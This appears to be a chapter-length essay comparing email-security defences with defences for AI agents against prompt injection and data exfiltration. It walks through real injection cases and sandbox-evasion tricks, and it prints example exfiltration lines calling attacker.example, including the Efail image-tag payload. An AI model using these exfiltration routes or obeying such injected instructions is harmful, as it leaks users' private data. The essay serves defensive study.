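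Some hidden text is legitimate, such as the preview lines in marketing emails and the image descriptions that blind people rely on. An agent can usually do without the preview lines but may need the image descriptions. Deleting invisible characters can also damage the flag emojis that caused Microsoft's false matches. These losses are small compared with quarantining a whole email.

The larger problem is that visibility is a matter of degree. An attacker can use text that a browser displays but a person is unlikely to notice, such as tiny text or grey text on a slightly lighter grey. Software can set minimum sizes and contrasts, but the attacker can stay just above them. A check of the HTML also misses text inside an image. Koide and colleagues found that models with better vision were more likely to read such faint text, so it may become more useful to attackers as models improve.

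Removing hidden text also doesn't stop visible lies, like the made-up conversation that fooled the summariser in Ahmed's report. A phishing detector shouldn't discard hidden text without recording that it was there, because its presence is evidence of phishing. Code can report that an email contains a hidden paragraph without showing the paragraph to a model.

### Which signals exist for agents

An agent that reads a company mailbox benefits from the provider's spam filter, which uses sender history and campaign data. Much of that information is missing for text from other sources.

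| Signal | Email | Web page | Shared document |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source | Domain, if authenticated | Website, but often not the author | Account that shared it, but not the author of each passage |
| History | Earlier mail from the sender | Reputation of the site | Often none |
| Volume | Similar messages in many mailboxes | One page can wait for many agents | Often a single copy |
| Reports from readers | Common | Rare | Rare |

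A website's reputation helps against a domain that someone registered last week to host an attack. It is little help in judging a comment or product review on a site that millions of people use, because a stranger who posts there benefits from the site's reputation. The spammers who moved to free mail services had to open thousands of accounts and keep replacing them, while someone who plants an injection in a popular page may need only one.

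Volume is also a weaker sign of an attack on agents than of spam. Spammers have to send many copies of a message because few people respond, and the copies make the spam easier to detect. An attacker can put text on a single web page and wait for an agent to read it, and the first agent to do so may be the intended target.

AI companies could recover some of this information. If a company's agents visit the same page for thousands of users and all begin to do something unrelated to their tasks, the company could notice and block the page for everyone. This would work like the "Report Spam" button, with the agents' behaviour in place of users' clicks. It would not help the first victims or catch a document written to attack a single company.

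The most valuable signals for filtering email are those that take an attacker time or money to build, such as a long correspondence with the company. A filter could use them to catch a fraudster who writes to the clerk from a new lookalike domain, whatever the email says, but not one who writes from the supplier's own mailbox.

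## Controlling links and images

An email that gets past the filter may still depend on a request to another computer. A link has no effect until someone opens it, and the sender learns nothing from a remote image until a program fetches it. Ordinary software can inspect or refuse these requests even if the reader already believes the email.

Suppose the fraudster's invoice email also has a link labelled "View our new payment details" that leads to a page on the lookalike domain brightpaper-billing.example.

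### URL rewriting, step by step

Microsoft sells a widely used rewriting service called Safe Links. With its recommended settings, the fraudster's link would go through four steps.

1. Before delivery, the mail system scans the link and replaces it with an address at Microsoft's checking service. The new address contains the old one: `https://nam01.safelinks.protection.outlook.com/?url=https%3A%2F%2Fbrightpaper-billing.example%2Fpay`
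2. The clerk clicks, and the browser contacts the checking service instead of the fraudster's site.
3. The service extracts the original address and compares it with a list of known malicious ones. If the address has no established reputation, the service also detonates the page in the background.
4. If the service considers the page malicious, the clerk sees a warning. Otherwise the service sends the browser on to the page.

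The service checks the page when the user clicks the link because the fraudster can change the page at any time. It might show a harmless notice about office hours when the email arrives at six in the morning, and a fake sign-in form by nine. Microsoft gives the example of an employee called Jim, whose IT department had turned off link rewriting and relied on a check that only some mail programs support. Jim used a program that didn't support it, clicked a link that had become malicious since delivery, and was fooled by the page.

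The service checks the linked page rather than the email's story, so it protects even a clerk who believes the email. But it has to recognise the page as malicious, and the first person to click may reach the page before the background scan finishes. Microsoft also advises companies to remove the option to continue past the warning, since a convinced clerk would use it.

### A trusted name on a hostile link

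Rewriting links can stop readers from seeing where a link goes, which phishing training tells them to check. The Australian Signals Directorate's cloud security guide, *Safe Links*, notes that administrators can hide the original link so that users can't copy it into a browser. Outlook reduces this problem by showing the original address when the reader hovers over the link. In a program without that feature, the reader sees a long address at a security company.

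That company's name can make a hostile link look safe, and attackers exploit this. According to LevelBlue's *Weaponizing Safe Links*, they break into a mailbox at an organization that uses a rewriting service, then email a malicious link from that mailbox to an account they control. The service wraps the link in its own domain. If it doesn't flag the page, the attackers copy the wrapped link into phishing emails to other organizations.

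Cloudflare's *Attackers abusing Proofpoint & Intermedia link wrapping to deliver phishing payloads* (2025) describes campaigns from June and July of that year. The emails posed as voicemail notices, secure messages and shared Teams documents, and the wrapped links led to fake Microsoft sign-in pages. Some attackers first shortened the link with a public URL shortener, which added another redirect. Filters that judge links by their domain's reputation did not help, because the wrapped links used a security company's domain. Cloudflare, which sells a competing email filter, says victims are much more likely to click a wrapped link than a bare one, but it gives no measurements.

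Attackers then began wrapping links several times. In LevelBlue's samples, phishing emails that used two or more rewriting services first appeared in the second quarter of 2024 and remained rare that year. They became more common throughout 2025 and surged in the last quarter. Chains of three or more services did not appear until mid-2025 and peaked in January 2026. One link went through six redirects at four security companies. LevelBlue sells email security too. Its counts come from sampled emails, so they show a trend but not what share of phishing uses the method.

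Each extra layer makes it harder for a scanner to work out the final destination, because every domain along the way belongs to a trusted company. In one campaign, the chain ended at a hacked website that forwarded visitors to a CAPTCHA, which kept automated scanners away from the fake sign-in page behind it. The link in that email was more than 1,200 characters long and partly encoded. LevelBlue advises companies to train staff to review URLs carefully, but few people could have found the destination in that one.

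### Why mail programs block remote images

An email can include an image that stays on the sender's server until the reader's mail program fetches it. From that request, the sender learns that someone opened the email and when, and can also learn the reader's IP address, mail program and operating system. Many mail programs therefore block remote images until the reader asks for them.

Some mail providers instead fetch images through their own servers and pass them on to the reader, so the sender sees the provider's IP address and not the reader's. But the provider's server still has to request the URL the sender wrote. If the sender gives each recipient a different image URL, a request for one can show which recipient opened the email.

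In 2018 researchers showed that an image request could reveal much more than that. Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues (2018), in *Efail*, attacked mail encrypted with S/MIME and OpenPGP, the two main standards for end-to-end encryption. The attacker needed a copy of an encrypted email, perhaps from a hacked mail server, but didn't need the key. The simplest version of the attack put the encrypted text between two scraps of HTML:

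| Part of the new email | Contents |
|---|---|
| 1 | `<img src="http://attacker.example/` |
| 2 | The stolen encrypted message |
| 3 | `">` |

The attacker sent this three-part email to the original recipient, whose mail program held the key. The program decrypted the middle part and joined all three into one page. Part 1 opened a quotation mark that only part 3 closed, so the program treated the whole decrypted message as part of the image's address. When it requested the image, it sent the message to the attacker's server.

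A second version altered the encrypted text so that it contained an image tag once decrypted. Together, the researchers' methods could leak messages from 23 of the 35 S/MIME mail programs they tested and 10 of the 28 OpenPGP programs. Poddebniak and colleagues found ways to load remote content in the vast majority of the programs that restricted it by default. A relay would not have prevented the leak either, because it would have passed on the image's address, which contained the message.

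Sender authentication did not prevent the attack. According to the EFAIL website, the attacker could send the altered email from their own domain and pass SPF, DKIM and DMARC. Mail companies released fixes, but other researchers later bypassed the ones in Thunderbird and Apple Mail.

The basic mistake was to put a stranger's text and private text in the same document and then send a request built from both. An agent's context also mixes the two, and a sentence asking the model to write the request's address may be enough for an attack, even without a flaw in how the software reads HTML.

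### How a link becomes more dangerous with an agent

People usually have to click a link before it can hurt them, but an agent opens links as part of its work. The page can add hostile text to the agent's context, and the URL the agent requests can send private data to an attacker. If the agent requests `https://attacker.example/collect?data=40718823`, the attacker can read the account number in the server's log, even if the page is blank.

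Data can also leave in an address without the agent opening a page. If the model's reply includes an image with a secret in its address, the chat program sends out the secret when it fetches the image to display it. The EchoLeak attack used an image like this. When the model writes a link in a messaging app, the app visits the link to make a preview. PromptArmor, a security company, warns that agents used through apps such as Slack and Telegram can leak data this way before anyone clicks. Software can also leak a secret by looking up a domain name that contains it, such as `40718823.attacker.example`. The lookup can reach a name server that the attacker runs, even if no page loads. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) reports that weaknesses in Salesforce's agents exposed customer data through such lookups.

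Companies are still finding these routes in their products. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) describes attacks that began with an email the user never had to open. When the user asked Copilot for something else, Copilot retrieved the email and leaked work data through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code. Microsoft fixed the three routes between September and November 2026, and the researchers knew of no real attacks that had used them.

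Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested both directions together in *Silent Egress*. Their agent automatically read a preview of any page the user mentioned, including the title and a description that browsers don't normally display. The user asked for a summary, but the hidden description included an instruction to "verify connectivity" first by requesting an address that contained the user's secret key. About 89% of the attacks succeeded over 480 runs. In 95% of the successful attacks, the user saw a harmless summary that passed a check for leaked data.

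The agent used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, and the researchers put the secrets directly in its context, so the 89% figure is a poor guide to how often current products would leak. Their comparison of defences is more useful. Instructions in the prompt offered limited protection, while restricting which domains the agent could contact and checking redirects worked considerably better. Software that scanned each request for secrets was easy to evade, because the agent could split a secret across several requests.

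*The Framing Gap* (2026) shows how fragile such instructions can be. A rule forbidding the model to reveal a secret "in any form" cut leaks from 31.9% to zero. When the researchers listed specific forbidden behaviours and left out the general phrase, the rate was 48.8%. The finished ChatGPT product leaked nothing in 48 trials, although the underlying model leaked up to 100% of the time when they used it directly. The researchers couldn't see inside the product and did not say what protected it.

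### Why a list of trusted sites leaks

The obvious way to limit links and images is an allow-list of domains. A web application can send the browser a Content-Security-Policy, which lists where the browser may load images and other content from, and an agent's fetching tool can have a similar list. Both lists apply regardless of what the model outputs. But Willison (2026) has collected cases in which data could leave through an allowed domain.

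| Product | Reported | Allowed destination | How data could get out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Salesforce Agentforce | September 2025 | An old domain for Salesforce images | The domain had expired, and researchers registered it |
| Google Antigravity | November 2025 | webhook.site | Anyone can create an address there that records requests |
| Superhuman AI | January 2026 | docs.google.com | Loading an "image" could submit data to an attacker's Google Form |
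| Claude Cowork | January 2026 | Anthropic's own API | The agent could upload files using an attacker's account key |

The expired domain was an error in maintaining the list, and webhook.site was a poor choice. The other two destinations are harder to rule out because they belong to reputable companies that accept data from the public. A domain check only establishes who runs the server, so an attacker can get around it with an account there.

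OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two more reasons not to rely on such lists. Many reputable sites have redirects, so a link to a trusted domain can lead to the attacker's site. A short list would also block much of the web, and people would get used to clicking through the constant warnings. Attackers can also use trusted domains in incoming links. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* describes an attack on Copilot that started with a link to microsoft.com, which URL filters were unlikely to flag.

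### OpenAI's public-URL check

OpenAI's alternative, published in January 2026, ignores the site's reputation and checks the whole address.

1. A crawler explores the public web as a search engine does and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When an agent is about to load a page or image automatically, software compares the full address with the crawler's records.
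3. If the address matches one exactly, the agent can load it.
4. If it doesn't match, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation. The user can then decide whether to open it.

Suppose the crawler has recorded `brightpaper.example/contact`. An injection then causes the accounts assistant to request `brightpaper.example/contact?note=40718823`, where the number is the company's own bank account. A domain list would approve both addresses, but the exact check blocks the second because the crawler never recorded it.

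An address can carry a secret in its text only if it changes when the secret changes. The crawler recorded its addresses without access to the conversation, so they would be the same whatever the account number was. The only exception is a secret that had already leaked onto the public web. An attacker can't get around the check by redirecting through a trusted site, because the secret would have to be in the starting address, which would then no longer match any address the crawler recorded.

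The model takes no part in the comparison, so the check still works after an injection has completely deceived the model. The warning in step 4 is weaker because OpenAI leaves the decision to a person, whom the email may also have deceived. Refusing the link is safer. In phishing experiments by Petelka and colleagues, people also did better when the warning disabled the original link.

### What an attacker can say with public addresses

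An attacker who can't put a secret in an address can still learn something from which address the agent chooses. Radware's *ZombieAgent* used this to get past an earlier ChatGPT safeguard that let the agent open addresses only exactly as it had received them. The attacker emailed a list of ready-made addresses, one for each letter and digit, and told the agent to spell out the secret by visiting the matching addresses in order. The server's log of those visits then revealed the secret, even though the agent hadn't altered any address. Radware reported the attack in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it that December.

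The public-URL check makes this harder because the crawler must already have recorded every address on the list. But in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, security researcher Johann Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably already has 36 recorded pages, one for each letter and digit. An injection can tell the model which page stands for which character. Rehberger adds that OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its technical paper.

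A choice among N addresses conveys at most log₂ N bits, and k requests in a known order can distinguish N^k messages. An eight-digit account number has 10⁸ possible values, so the number of requests an attacker needs to leak it depends on how many recorded pages they have.

| Recorded pages available | Most information per request | Requests for an eight-digit number |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 bit | 27 |
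| 10 | 3.3 bits | 8 |
| 100 | 6.6 bits | 4 |
| 10,000 | 13.3 bits | 2 |

Copying out a mailbox this way would take a huge number of requests, but copying out an account number would take far fewer. One request is enough to reveal a single-bit secret, such as whether a company has accepted a takeover offer.

Rehberger suggests stopping an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or saving the first response and reusing it. Either would hinder an attacker who needs the agent to request the page for "7" three times. Radware's attack already partly avoided this limit by using separate addresses for each position in the message. With 80 recorded pages, an attacker could give every digit in every position its own page. The agent would then visit each page at most once, and the requests could arrive in any order.

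Anthropic had a similar problem with a different rule. Its chatbot Claude could open only addresses that the user had typed, that a web search had returned or that appeared on pages it had already fetched. According to Willison, Ayush Paul built a site where each page linked to further pages, one for each letter, and told Claude that it had to follow them to find the user's profile. Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer by following the links. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links on the pages it fetches. That blocks this attack, but it also prevents Claude from using the tool to follow useful links.

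### What the check leaves open

OpenAI promises only that an agent won't quietly leak a user's data through the address itself. A public page in the crawler's record can still contain lies, instructions or other harmful content, and it may have changed since it was crawled. OpenAI therefore treats the check as one layer among several.

The software also makes exceptions. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT treats any address in the user's own message as safe for the rest of the session. This is reasonable when a person has typed the address, but it would be risky in an application that pastes an incoming email into the user's message, because the attacker's addresses would then count as the user's. Willison made the same point about Anthropic's tool in 2025.

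Rehberger's last concern is that even a good check can't protect a product that doesn't use it. He reported image leaks to OpenAI in early 2023, and OpenAI added its first safeguard in December 2023 but left it out of the macOS and iOS apps. Data can also leak through a series of programs. In May 2026 Willison described how Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without asking for approval. A deceived agent could write a message containing an image whose address held a link to one of the user's files, and the data would leak when the user opened the message. A check on the agent's web tool wouldn't cover that request, because a mail program makes it. A check that runs only when a page loads also couldn't stop a secret that had already leaked through a domain lookup.

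OpenAI now also offers a stricter setting called Lockdown Mode. Willison reports that it limits outbound network requests to prevent the final step of a leak.

### The invoice link in both systems

The fraudster's email, with its link to `brightpaper-billing.example/pay`, reaches the clerk at six in the morning. The mail system scans the page, finds nothing and rewrites the link so that clicks go through a checking service. When the clerk clicks at nine, the service checks the page again. If the page has become a fake sign-in form and someone has reported it, the clerk sees a warning. If the page only shows a new account number, the service will probably let the clerk through, because there is no malicious code or password form to detect.

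Now suppose the assistant tries to open the link and OpenAI's check is in place. The fraudster registered the domain yesterday and the crawler hasn't recorded the page, so the software refuses to load it or asks the clerk. A more patient fraudster could publish the page weeks earlier and wait for the crawler to record it. The assistant would then load the page and read the false bank details. If the fraudster also hid an instruction on the page to send back the company's account balance in a web address, the check would stop that request, but the fraudster might still get paid.

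The check could treat the real supplier's link like the fraudster's new page, because suppliers often give each invoice its own private address, which a public crawler should never have seen. An accounts assistant would run into this problem every day, and a clerk who approves forty genuine invoice links may approve the next one without reading it. The company could instead let the assistant fetch invoices through a separate connection to the supplier's billing system.

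The two systems also interfere with each other. Safe Links rewrites links separately for each recipient, so public crawlers are unlikely to have recorded the address in the assistant's copy of the email. The agent's software would have to extract the original address before comparing it, and would then bypass the checking service unless it also had that service check the page. Both checks are worth doing, because the checking service looks for malicious pages and OpenAI's check looks for private data in the address. Neither can verify whether the account number on the page belongs to Bright Paper.

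## Test-running content in a sandbox

Defenders can also find out what a file or page does by running it where it can't cause harm. In email security, this is called detonation. Nobody has to judge whether the email's story is true, because the test records only what the content does. But the test works only if the content behaves as it would on the clerk's computer, so attackers try to make it behave differently in the sandbox.

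### How detonation works

Microsoft's Safe Attachments is a typical example. After an ordinary antivirus scan, it opens the attachment in a virtual machine, a simulated computer kept apart from the company's real ones. According to *Python and Malware* (2021), such tests record which files the attachment reads or changes, along with its network connections, Windows registry changes, operating system calls and memory use.

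The software then uses this record to judge whether the file is malicious. An invoice that only displays an account number adds little to the record. If the invoice starts a script, downloads a program and sets that program to run whenever the computer starts, it is probably malware, even if no antivirus company has seen the file before. Single actions are often ambiguous, since legitimate installers also download programs and change settings.

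Microsoft's scan usually takes up to 15 minutes, and sometimes longer. Under the default setting, Block, the system holds the whole email until the scan finishes. If the scan finds a threat, the system quarantines the email and blocks later copies. By default, only an administrator can release the quarantined email.

A company that doesn't want to delay its mail can choose Dynamic Delivery. The clerk receives the text of the email immediately, with a placeholder for each attachment, and can safely preview most PDFs and Office documents while the test runs. An AI assistant that reads the email during those minutes may also find only a placeholder. Unless its software checks again later, the assistant may report that the supplier forgot the invoice.

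In 2024 Microsoft announced that it was ending another option, Monitor, which delivered dangerous attachments and tracked what happened to them. It recommended Block instead. Microsoft also test-runs links in a sandbox.

### Files that recognise or outlast the test

A malicious file can pass by doing nothing during the test, most simply by waiting. *Command & Control* (2014) explains that a system with many files to analyse can spend only a few minutes on each. Attackers can also write code that runs 100 times slower under observation than on an ordinary computer, so the test ends before anything malicious happens.

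Sandbox developers responded by speeding up the clock, so that a file programmed to sleep for an hour woke almost at once. *Malware Dynamic Analysis Evasion Techniques* (2018) describes how this could backfire. Some malware waited a set time for user activity and stayed inactive if there was none. With the clock running fast, the wait ended early and the file looked harmless. Other malware detected the faster clock by comparing the length of the sleep with a counter in the processor.

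A file can also check whether it is running in a sandbox. Early malware searched for traces of the virtual machine software, and defenders removed or disguised them. Later malware looked for signs of everyday use. *A Measurement Study of AI-Environment Realism Gaps in Malware-Analysis Sandboxes* (2026) lists browser history, event logs, personal files and mouse movements among things that a real computer accumulates and a freshly reset sandbox lacks. Defenders now fabricate some of this history. They can also test files on real computers, but *Python and Malware* describes that as too slow for the number of files.

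Some malware acts only under narrower conditions, such as between certain dates, for a particular username or at a particular network address. A realistic sandbox doesn't help much if the file acts only on one specific employee's account.

Other files and pages need a person's help before they do anything. The locked attachment that Barracuda found needs a password, and the fake sign-in page in LevelBlue's example sat behind a CAPTCHA. When Microsoft test-runs locked files in SharePoint, OneDrive and Teams, it tries a list of known passwords and patterns, which may not include a password the attacker made up for one email.

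### Detonation and containment

People use "sandboxing" for two jobs. Detonation runs the content in advance to decide whether to deliver it. Containment limits the damage the content can do while someone uses it for real work, for instance by letting a clerk open every attachment in an isolated program that can't reach the company's files.

A file that does nothing for its first 15 minutes passes detonation, and the clerk receives it as safe. Containment still applies when the file becomes active an hour later. A company that runs its agent in a restricted environment has containment, but that doesn't mean the emails the agent reads have been tested.

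Ordinary detonation doesn't detect prompt injection, because the sandbox has no language model for the text to influence. A test for injections has to give the text to a model and observe its response.

### CheckTool

CheckTool, from *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing*, is the simplest such test. When a tool returns an email or a web page, the software first shows it to a model and checks whether the model calls a tool. If it doesn't, the software passes the text to the agent. If it does, the software can reject the text, or return it to the model with the name of the called tool and an instruction to delete whatever prompted the call.

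The researchers tested it on AgentDojo. The attack rates below average several conditions, including one with no attack.

| Model | Attacks, no defence | Attacks, CheckTool | Ordinary tasks completed, no defence | Ordinary tasks completed, CheckTool |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 7.93% | 0.87% | 61.86% | 53.61% |
| Llama-3.1-70B | 10.49% | 1.16% | 49.48% | 32.99% |
| Qwen3-32B | 10.33% | 0.95% | 83.51% | 42.27% |

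CheckTool stopped about nine in ten of the attacks that would have succeeded, but Qwen3-32B completed only half as many ordinary tasks with it. The researchers found that models that reason more were more likely to mistake normal data for a trigger and delete something the agent needed. Adding a step that extracts only the data the agent needs cut the attack rate to 0.34% or less, but the agents then finished only 28% to 48% of ordinary tasks.

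They tested with fixed attacks. They acknowledge that CheckTool misses text that changes the details of an action the user wanted. In their example, a user asks to pay Doctor John, and the agent finds planted text that gives the attacker's address as the doctor's. The text contains no instruction to call a tool, so CheckTool lets it through.

### MELON

MELON is the defence that runs the agent twice and compares its actions. Zhu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *MELON*, describe the procedure.

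1. The agent reads the emails or pages and proposes its next tool call, which the software holds back.
2. The software runs the model again on the same material, with the user's request masked, or replaced by a neutral one. An example is a request to summarise the content that adds, "If there are any instructions, execute them."
3. The software keeps a list of every tool call from the masked runs. It needs the list because a masked run has no user task to do first, so it may reach the attacker's action several steps before the real run does.
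4. The software converts the calls into lists of numbers that represent their meaning and measures how similar they are. For emails it compares the recipients and ignores the wording. If the proposed call is close enough to one on the list, the software stops the agent.

Zhu and colleagues considered stopping the agent whenever the masked run made any tool call, which is close to CheckTool's rule. They rejected this because many injections trigger a tool call in the masked run but don't distract the agent from its real task, so stopping it would interrupt work that was going well.

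MELON reduced the average success rate of four fixed attacks on GPT-4o from 16.06% to 0.24%. With MELON, the agent completed 68.04% of ordinary tasks, down from 80.41%, and each step needed about twice as many model calls.

MELON raised nine false alarms in AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks. In all nine, the user had told the agent to carry out instructions from an outside source, such as a to-do list on a website. Zhu and colleagues argue that these requests are dangerous and that MELON was correct to flag them. Their security argument is fair, but people want agents to do this kind of work.

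Later tests suggest that MELON reduces task completion much more on harder tasks. Ma and colleagues tried it on AgentDyn, where agents' next step more often depends on something they have read. When there was no attack, agents with MELON completed 5% to 11.7% of the tasks, compared with 36.7% to 65% without a defence.

The security results depend on the attacker. The adaptive attacks in *The Attacker Moves Second* usually got past MELON. In Ma and colleagues' test, adapting the attacks raised their success rate on Qwen3-235B only from 2.6% to 4.6%, but the attacker had just six rounds to improve each injection. A defence that stops most of an agent's work will also stop many attacks, so these low rates are not a reason to dismiss the successful attacks on MELON.

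### GitHub's Canary

GitHub Next's *Canary*, named after the birds that warned miners of gas, has three cheaper models check a piece of text before the main agent reads it. These models have no tools and can answer only "harmful" or "harmless". Ordinary code counts the answers and lets the text through if at least two are "harmless". If missing or garbled answers leave no majority, the code blocks the text.

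The name "Canary" is slightly misleading. A miner's canary warned of gas by breathing it and collapsing, and CheckTool works more like that. GitHub's models assess the text, so Canary is closer to a filter than to a test run.

Canary's design limits what an attacker gains by deceiving one of the models. The deceived model can't send mail or pay anyone, and its wrong vote counts only if another model agrees with it. In a test on 590 inputs, half of them harmful, the best trio missed four harmful inputs and blocked no harmless ones. Claude Opus 4.8, a more expensive model working alone, missed three harmful inputs.

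Canary raised no false alarms in 295 attempts on harmless inputs, but the true rate could still be about 1%, which is too high when attacks are rare. Most of the inputs were changes to software packages. The harmless conversations were copies of the attacked ones with the injections removed, so they are weak evidence of how Canary would treat a supplier's urgent but honest request. GitHub Next did not test attackers who adapt to the vote.

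### The odds of passing a test

A model can respond differently to the same text each time, so an injection may fail in a test run and succeed in the real one. Suppose it fires, meaning that it makes the model take the attacker's action, with probability p in each run. If the software does k test runs first and blocks the text when any of them fires, the attack succeeds only if all k tests stay quiet and the real run fires:

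P(success) = p(1 − p)^k

The attacker wants p to be high for the real run and low for the tests. The derivative of the formula is (1 − p)^(k−1) × [1 − (k + 1)p], which is zero at p = 1/(k + 1). With one test, the attacker's best injection fires half the time and succeeds 0.5 × 0.5 = 25% of the time.

| Test runs | Attacker's best p | Success rate at the best p | Success rate if p is 90% |
|---|---|---|---|
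| 0 | 100% | 100% | 90% |
| 1 | 50% | 25% | 9% |
| 2 | 33.3% | 14.8% | 0.9% |
| 5 | 16.7% | 6.7% | 0.0009% |
| 10 | 9.1% | 3.5% | less than 0.0001% |

Test runs are therefore very good at catching reliable injections. An attacker does better with an unreliable one, but even the best of these succeeds only 6.7% of the time against five test runs.

The attacker can send more than one email. If each has a 6.7% chance of succeeding, ten separate attempts give about an even chance that at least one succeeds. But each attempt also has a 60% chance of setting off at least one of the five tests, so the company would expect about six of the ten emails to raise an alarm. It could stop the attack by responding to the first alarm, if it can connect the emails to one another.

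Running more tests also takes more computation and blocks more harmless texts. Five tests on each of a million texts a month add five million model runs. If each test has an independent 1% chance of a false alarm, and a single alarm blocks a text, five tests wrongly block 4.9% of harmless texts.

These figures assume that an injection is as likely to fire in a test as in the real run, and that the runs are independent. If it fires with probability p in each test and q in the real run, its success rate after k tests is q(1 − p)^k. An injection that never fires in tests but fires 90% of the time in real use succeeds 90% of the time, no matter how many tests the company runs.

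Zhu and colleagues' mathematical guarantee for MELON has the same weakness. They propose masking the request with n different neutral prompts and averaging the similarity scores. If the expected average for injected text is μ and the alarm threshold is θ, the chance of missing an attack is at most exp[−2n(μ − θ)²]. With 100 prompts, μ = 0.7 and θ = 0.5, that is about 3.4 in 10,000. (The paper gives 1.8 in 10,000, which doesn't match its formula.) The bound holds only if μ is above θ. When an injection stays inactive under every neutral prompt, adding prompts only makes MELON more certain to miss it.

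### Why the real run is different

Malware has to inspect the computer to work out whether it is in a sandbox, but an injection can state a condition and leave the model to check it. Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil is in the Context*, give the example of an invoice containing an instruction to send the invoice to the attacker only if the user asks to pay it. A test that asks for a summary doesn't meet the condition, so the injection does nothing.

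Files and injections can use similar conditions to get past a test:

| What is missing from the test | A file can wait for | An injection can wait for |
|---|---|---|
| The right person or task | A particular username | A request to pay the invoice |
| A response from a person | A click | The user's reply to a question |
| Signs of ordinary use | Browser history | Earlier mail from the supplier |
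| Enough time | The end of the test | A later conversation |

Chang and colleagues describe an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that combined two of these. A document about Albert Einstein contained an instruction to summarise it as requested and then ask whether the summary had helped. Whether the user answered yes or no, Copilot stored a malicious instruction in its memory, where it affected later conversations. A test that ended with the summary would not have revealed the attack.

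The test model also needs the tools an injection might target, because an instruction to make a payment can't cause a payment call if there is no payment tool. Fake tools help, but they have to return believable results. If the injected instruction is to find an employee's address in the inbox and send it somewhere, a test with an empty inbox may end before the agent tries to send anything.

An injection can also depend on other text. In an attack on the coding agent Devin, one web page told the agent to start a web server that exposed its files and then visit a second page, which told it to open the server to the internet and leak the address. Testing either page alone would show only part of the attack.

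To see how much such conditions matter, Chang and colleagues took 40 AgentDojo attacks that had all failed on GPT-5.6-Luna and had a model rewrite them. Each new version included a condition, stayed on the subject of the user's task and changed only the details or wording of what the agent did. Seven of the 40 rewritten attacks succeeded with no defence, and eight succeeded with MELON. The sample is too small for a difference of one to be meaningful, but there is no sign that MELON helped.

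Some injections depend on the user's task without stating a condition. *SecPO* (2026) examined 140 attacks that succeeded against a model trained to resist them, and found that many presented the attacker's action as a necessary step in the user's task. With the task masked, that claim may no longer make sense, so the model may not act on it. In 75 of the 140 cases, the agent also finished the user's task, so a test that checked only for task completion would have missed those attacks.

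The most realistic test is the real run, with each tool call held back until it has been checked. MELON does this, but its check relies on a masked run that the attacker can plan for.

### Attacks with no tool call

All of these tests except Canary's vote look for tool calls, so they can miss injections that only change what the agent writes. Zhu and colleagues examined 66 attacks that MELON missed. In 73% of them, the harm was in the reply, for instance when the agent persuaded the user to buy something expensive. In another 15%, the agent reused information it already had in the real run but made new calls to fetch it in the masked run, so the calls didn't match. The rest involved models that made up information or called tools that didn't exist.

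False answers also seem easier to cause than harmful actions. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) gave an automated attacker up to 64 attempts at each task. Against GPT-5.5, the attacker succeeded 81.43% of the time when it only had to change the answer and 28.52% when it had to make the agent change something in an application. Against Claude Sonnet 5, the rates were 40.57% and 7.90%. A test that checks only for actions therefore misses the attacks most likely to work.

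Replies can also leak data, and not only through image addresses. Chang and colleagues describe a spreadsheet with an instruction that took effect when the user asked about a customer named Johann. The model's answer included data from other rows, encoded in control characters. The Terminal program on the user's Mac interpreted those characters and made a domain lookup that sent the data out.

In the invoice example, the result of a MELON test could depend on how the fraudster words the email. If the fraudster writes "please pay $8,000 to this account", the masked run may also propose the payment, and MELON would stop the assistant. It could also block a payment to an honest supplier who wrote the same sentence. If the fraudster only mentions that the supplier has a new bank account, the masked run has no instruction to carry out, but the real run, which has the clerk's request to deal with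 the morning's invoices, pays the fraudster.

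## Limiting what a deceived reader can do

A company can limit in advance how much harm a deceived reader can do, in case filters, warnings and test runs all miss a fraudster's email. Email security has two good examples, one involving attachments and the other passwords. In both, companies spent years warning people about a dangerous action before software removed the option.

### Macros in attachments

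A macro is a small program inside an Office document. Criminals used to email documents whose macros installed malware. Office ran these macros only after the reader clicked "Enable Content" on a warning. Proofpoint's *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World* explains that the sender typically convinced the reader that the document was important and that viewing it required macros.

In 2022 Microsoft removed the button for enabling macros in files from the internet. According to Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office*, readers now see a notice that Office has blocked the macros, with a link to an explanation. They can still open the file's properties and tick "Unblock", unless their company's settings prevent it. The main rollout began on 27 July, and the slowest corporate update channel followed in January 2023.

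Windows attaches a label called the Mark of the Web to files from the internet, including email attachments. When someone opens a labelled file, Office checks whether it is in a folder the company trusts, whether a trusted publisher signed its macros and whether the company has a policy on macros. If none of these determines whether the macros can run, Office normally blocks them. The document's text has no effect on the decision, however persuasive it is.

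Proofpoint found that attackers' use of macro attachments fell by about 66% between October 2021 and June 2022. Microsoft had not yet begun the main rollout of its macro block, so attackers seem to have reacted to its announcements. Computer Weekly reports that macros had barely appeared in Proofpoint's data almost six months into 2023. The Record reports that Microsoft withdrew the block in July 2022 after some customers complained, then quickly reinstated it when security experts objected.

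Attackers also moved to other file types. Over the same nine months, campaigns using ISO files, which are disk images containing other files, rose by more than 150%, and those using Windows shortcut files rose by 1,675% from a low base. ISO files were useful because Windows put the Mark of the Web on the ISO file but not on the document inside, so Office didn't treat the document as coming from the internet. In early 2023 several groups tried attachments for OneNote, Microsoft's note-taking program. IBM saw very little of this after March and thinks this is probably because Microsoft blocked dangerous files embedded in OneNote documents.

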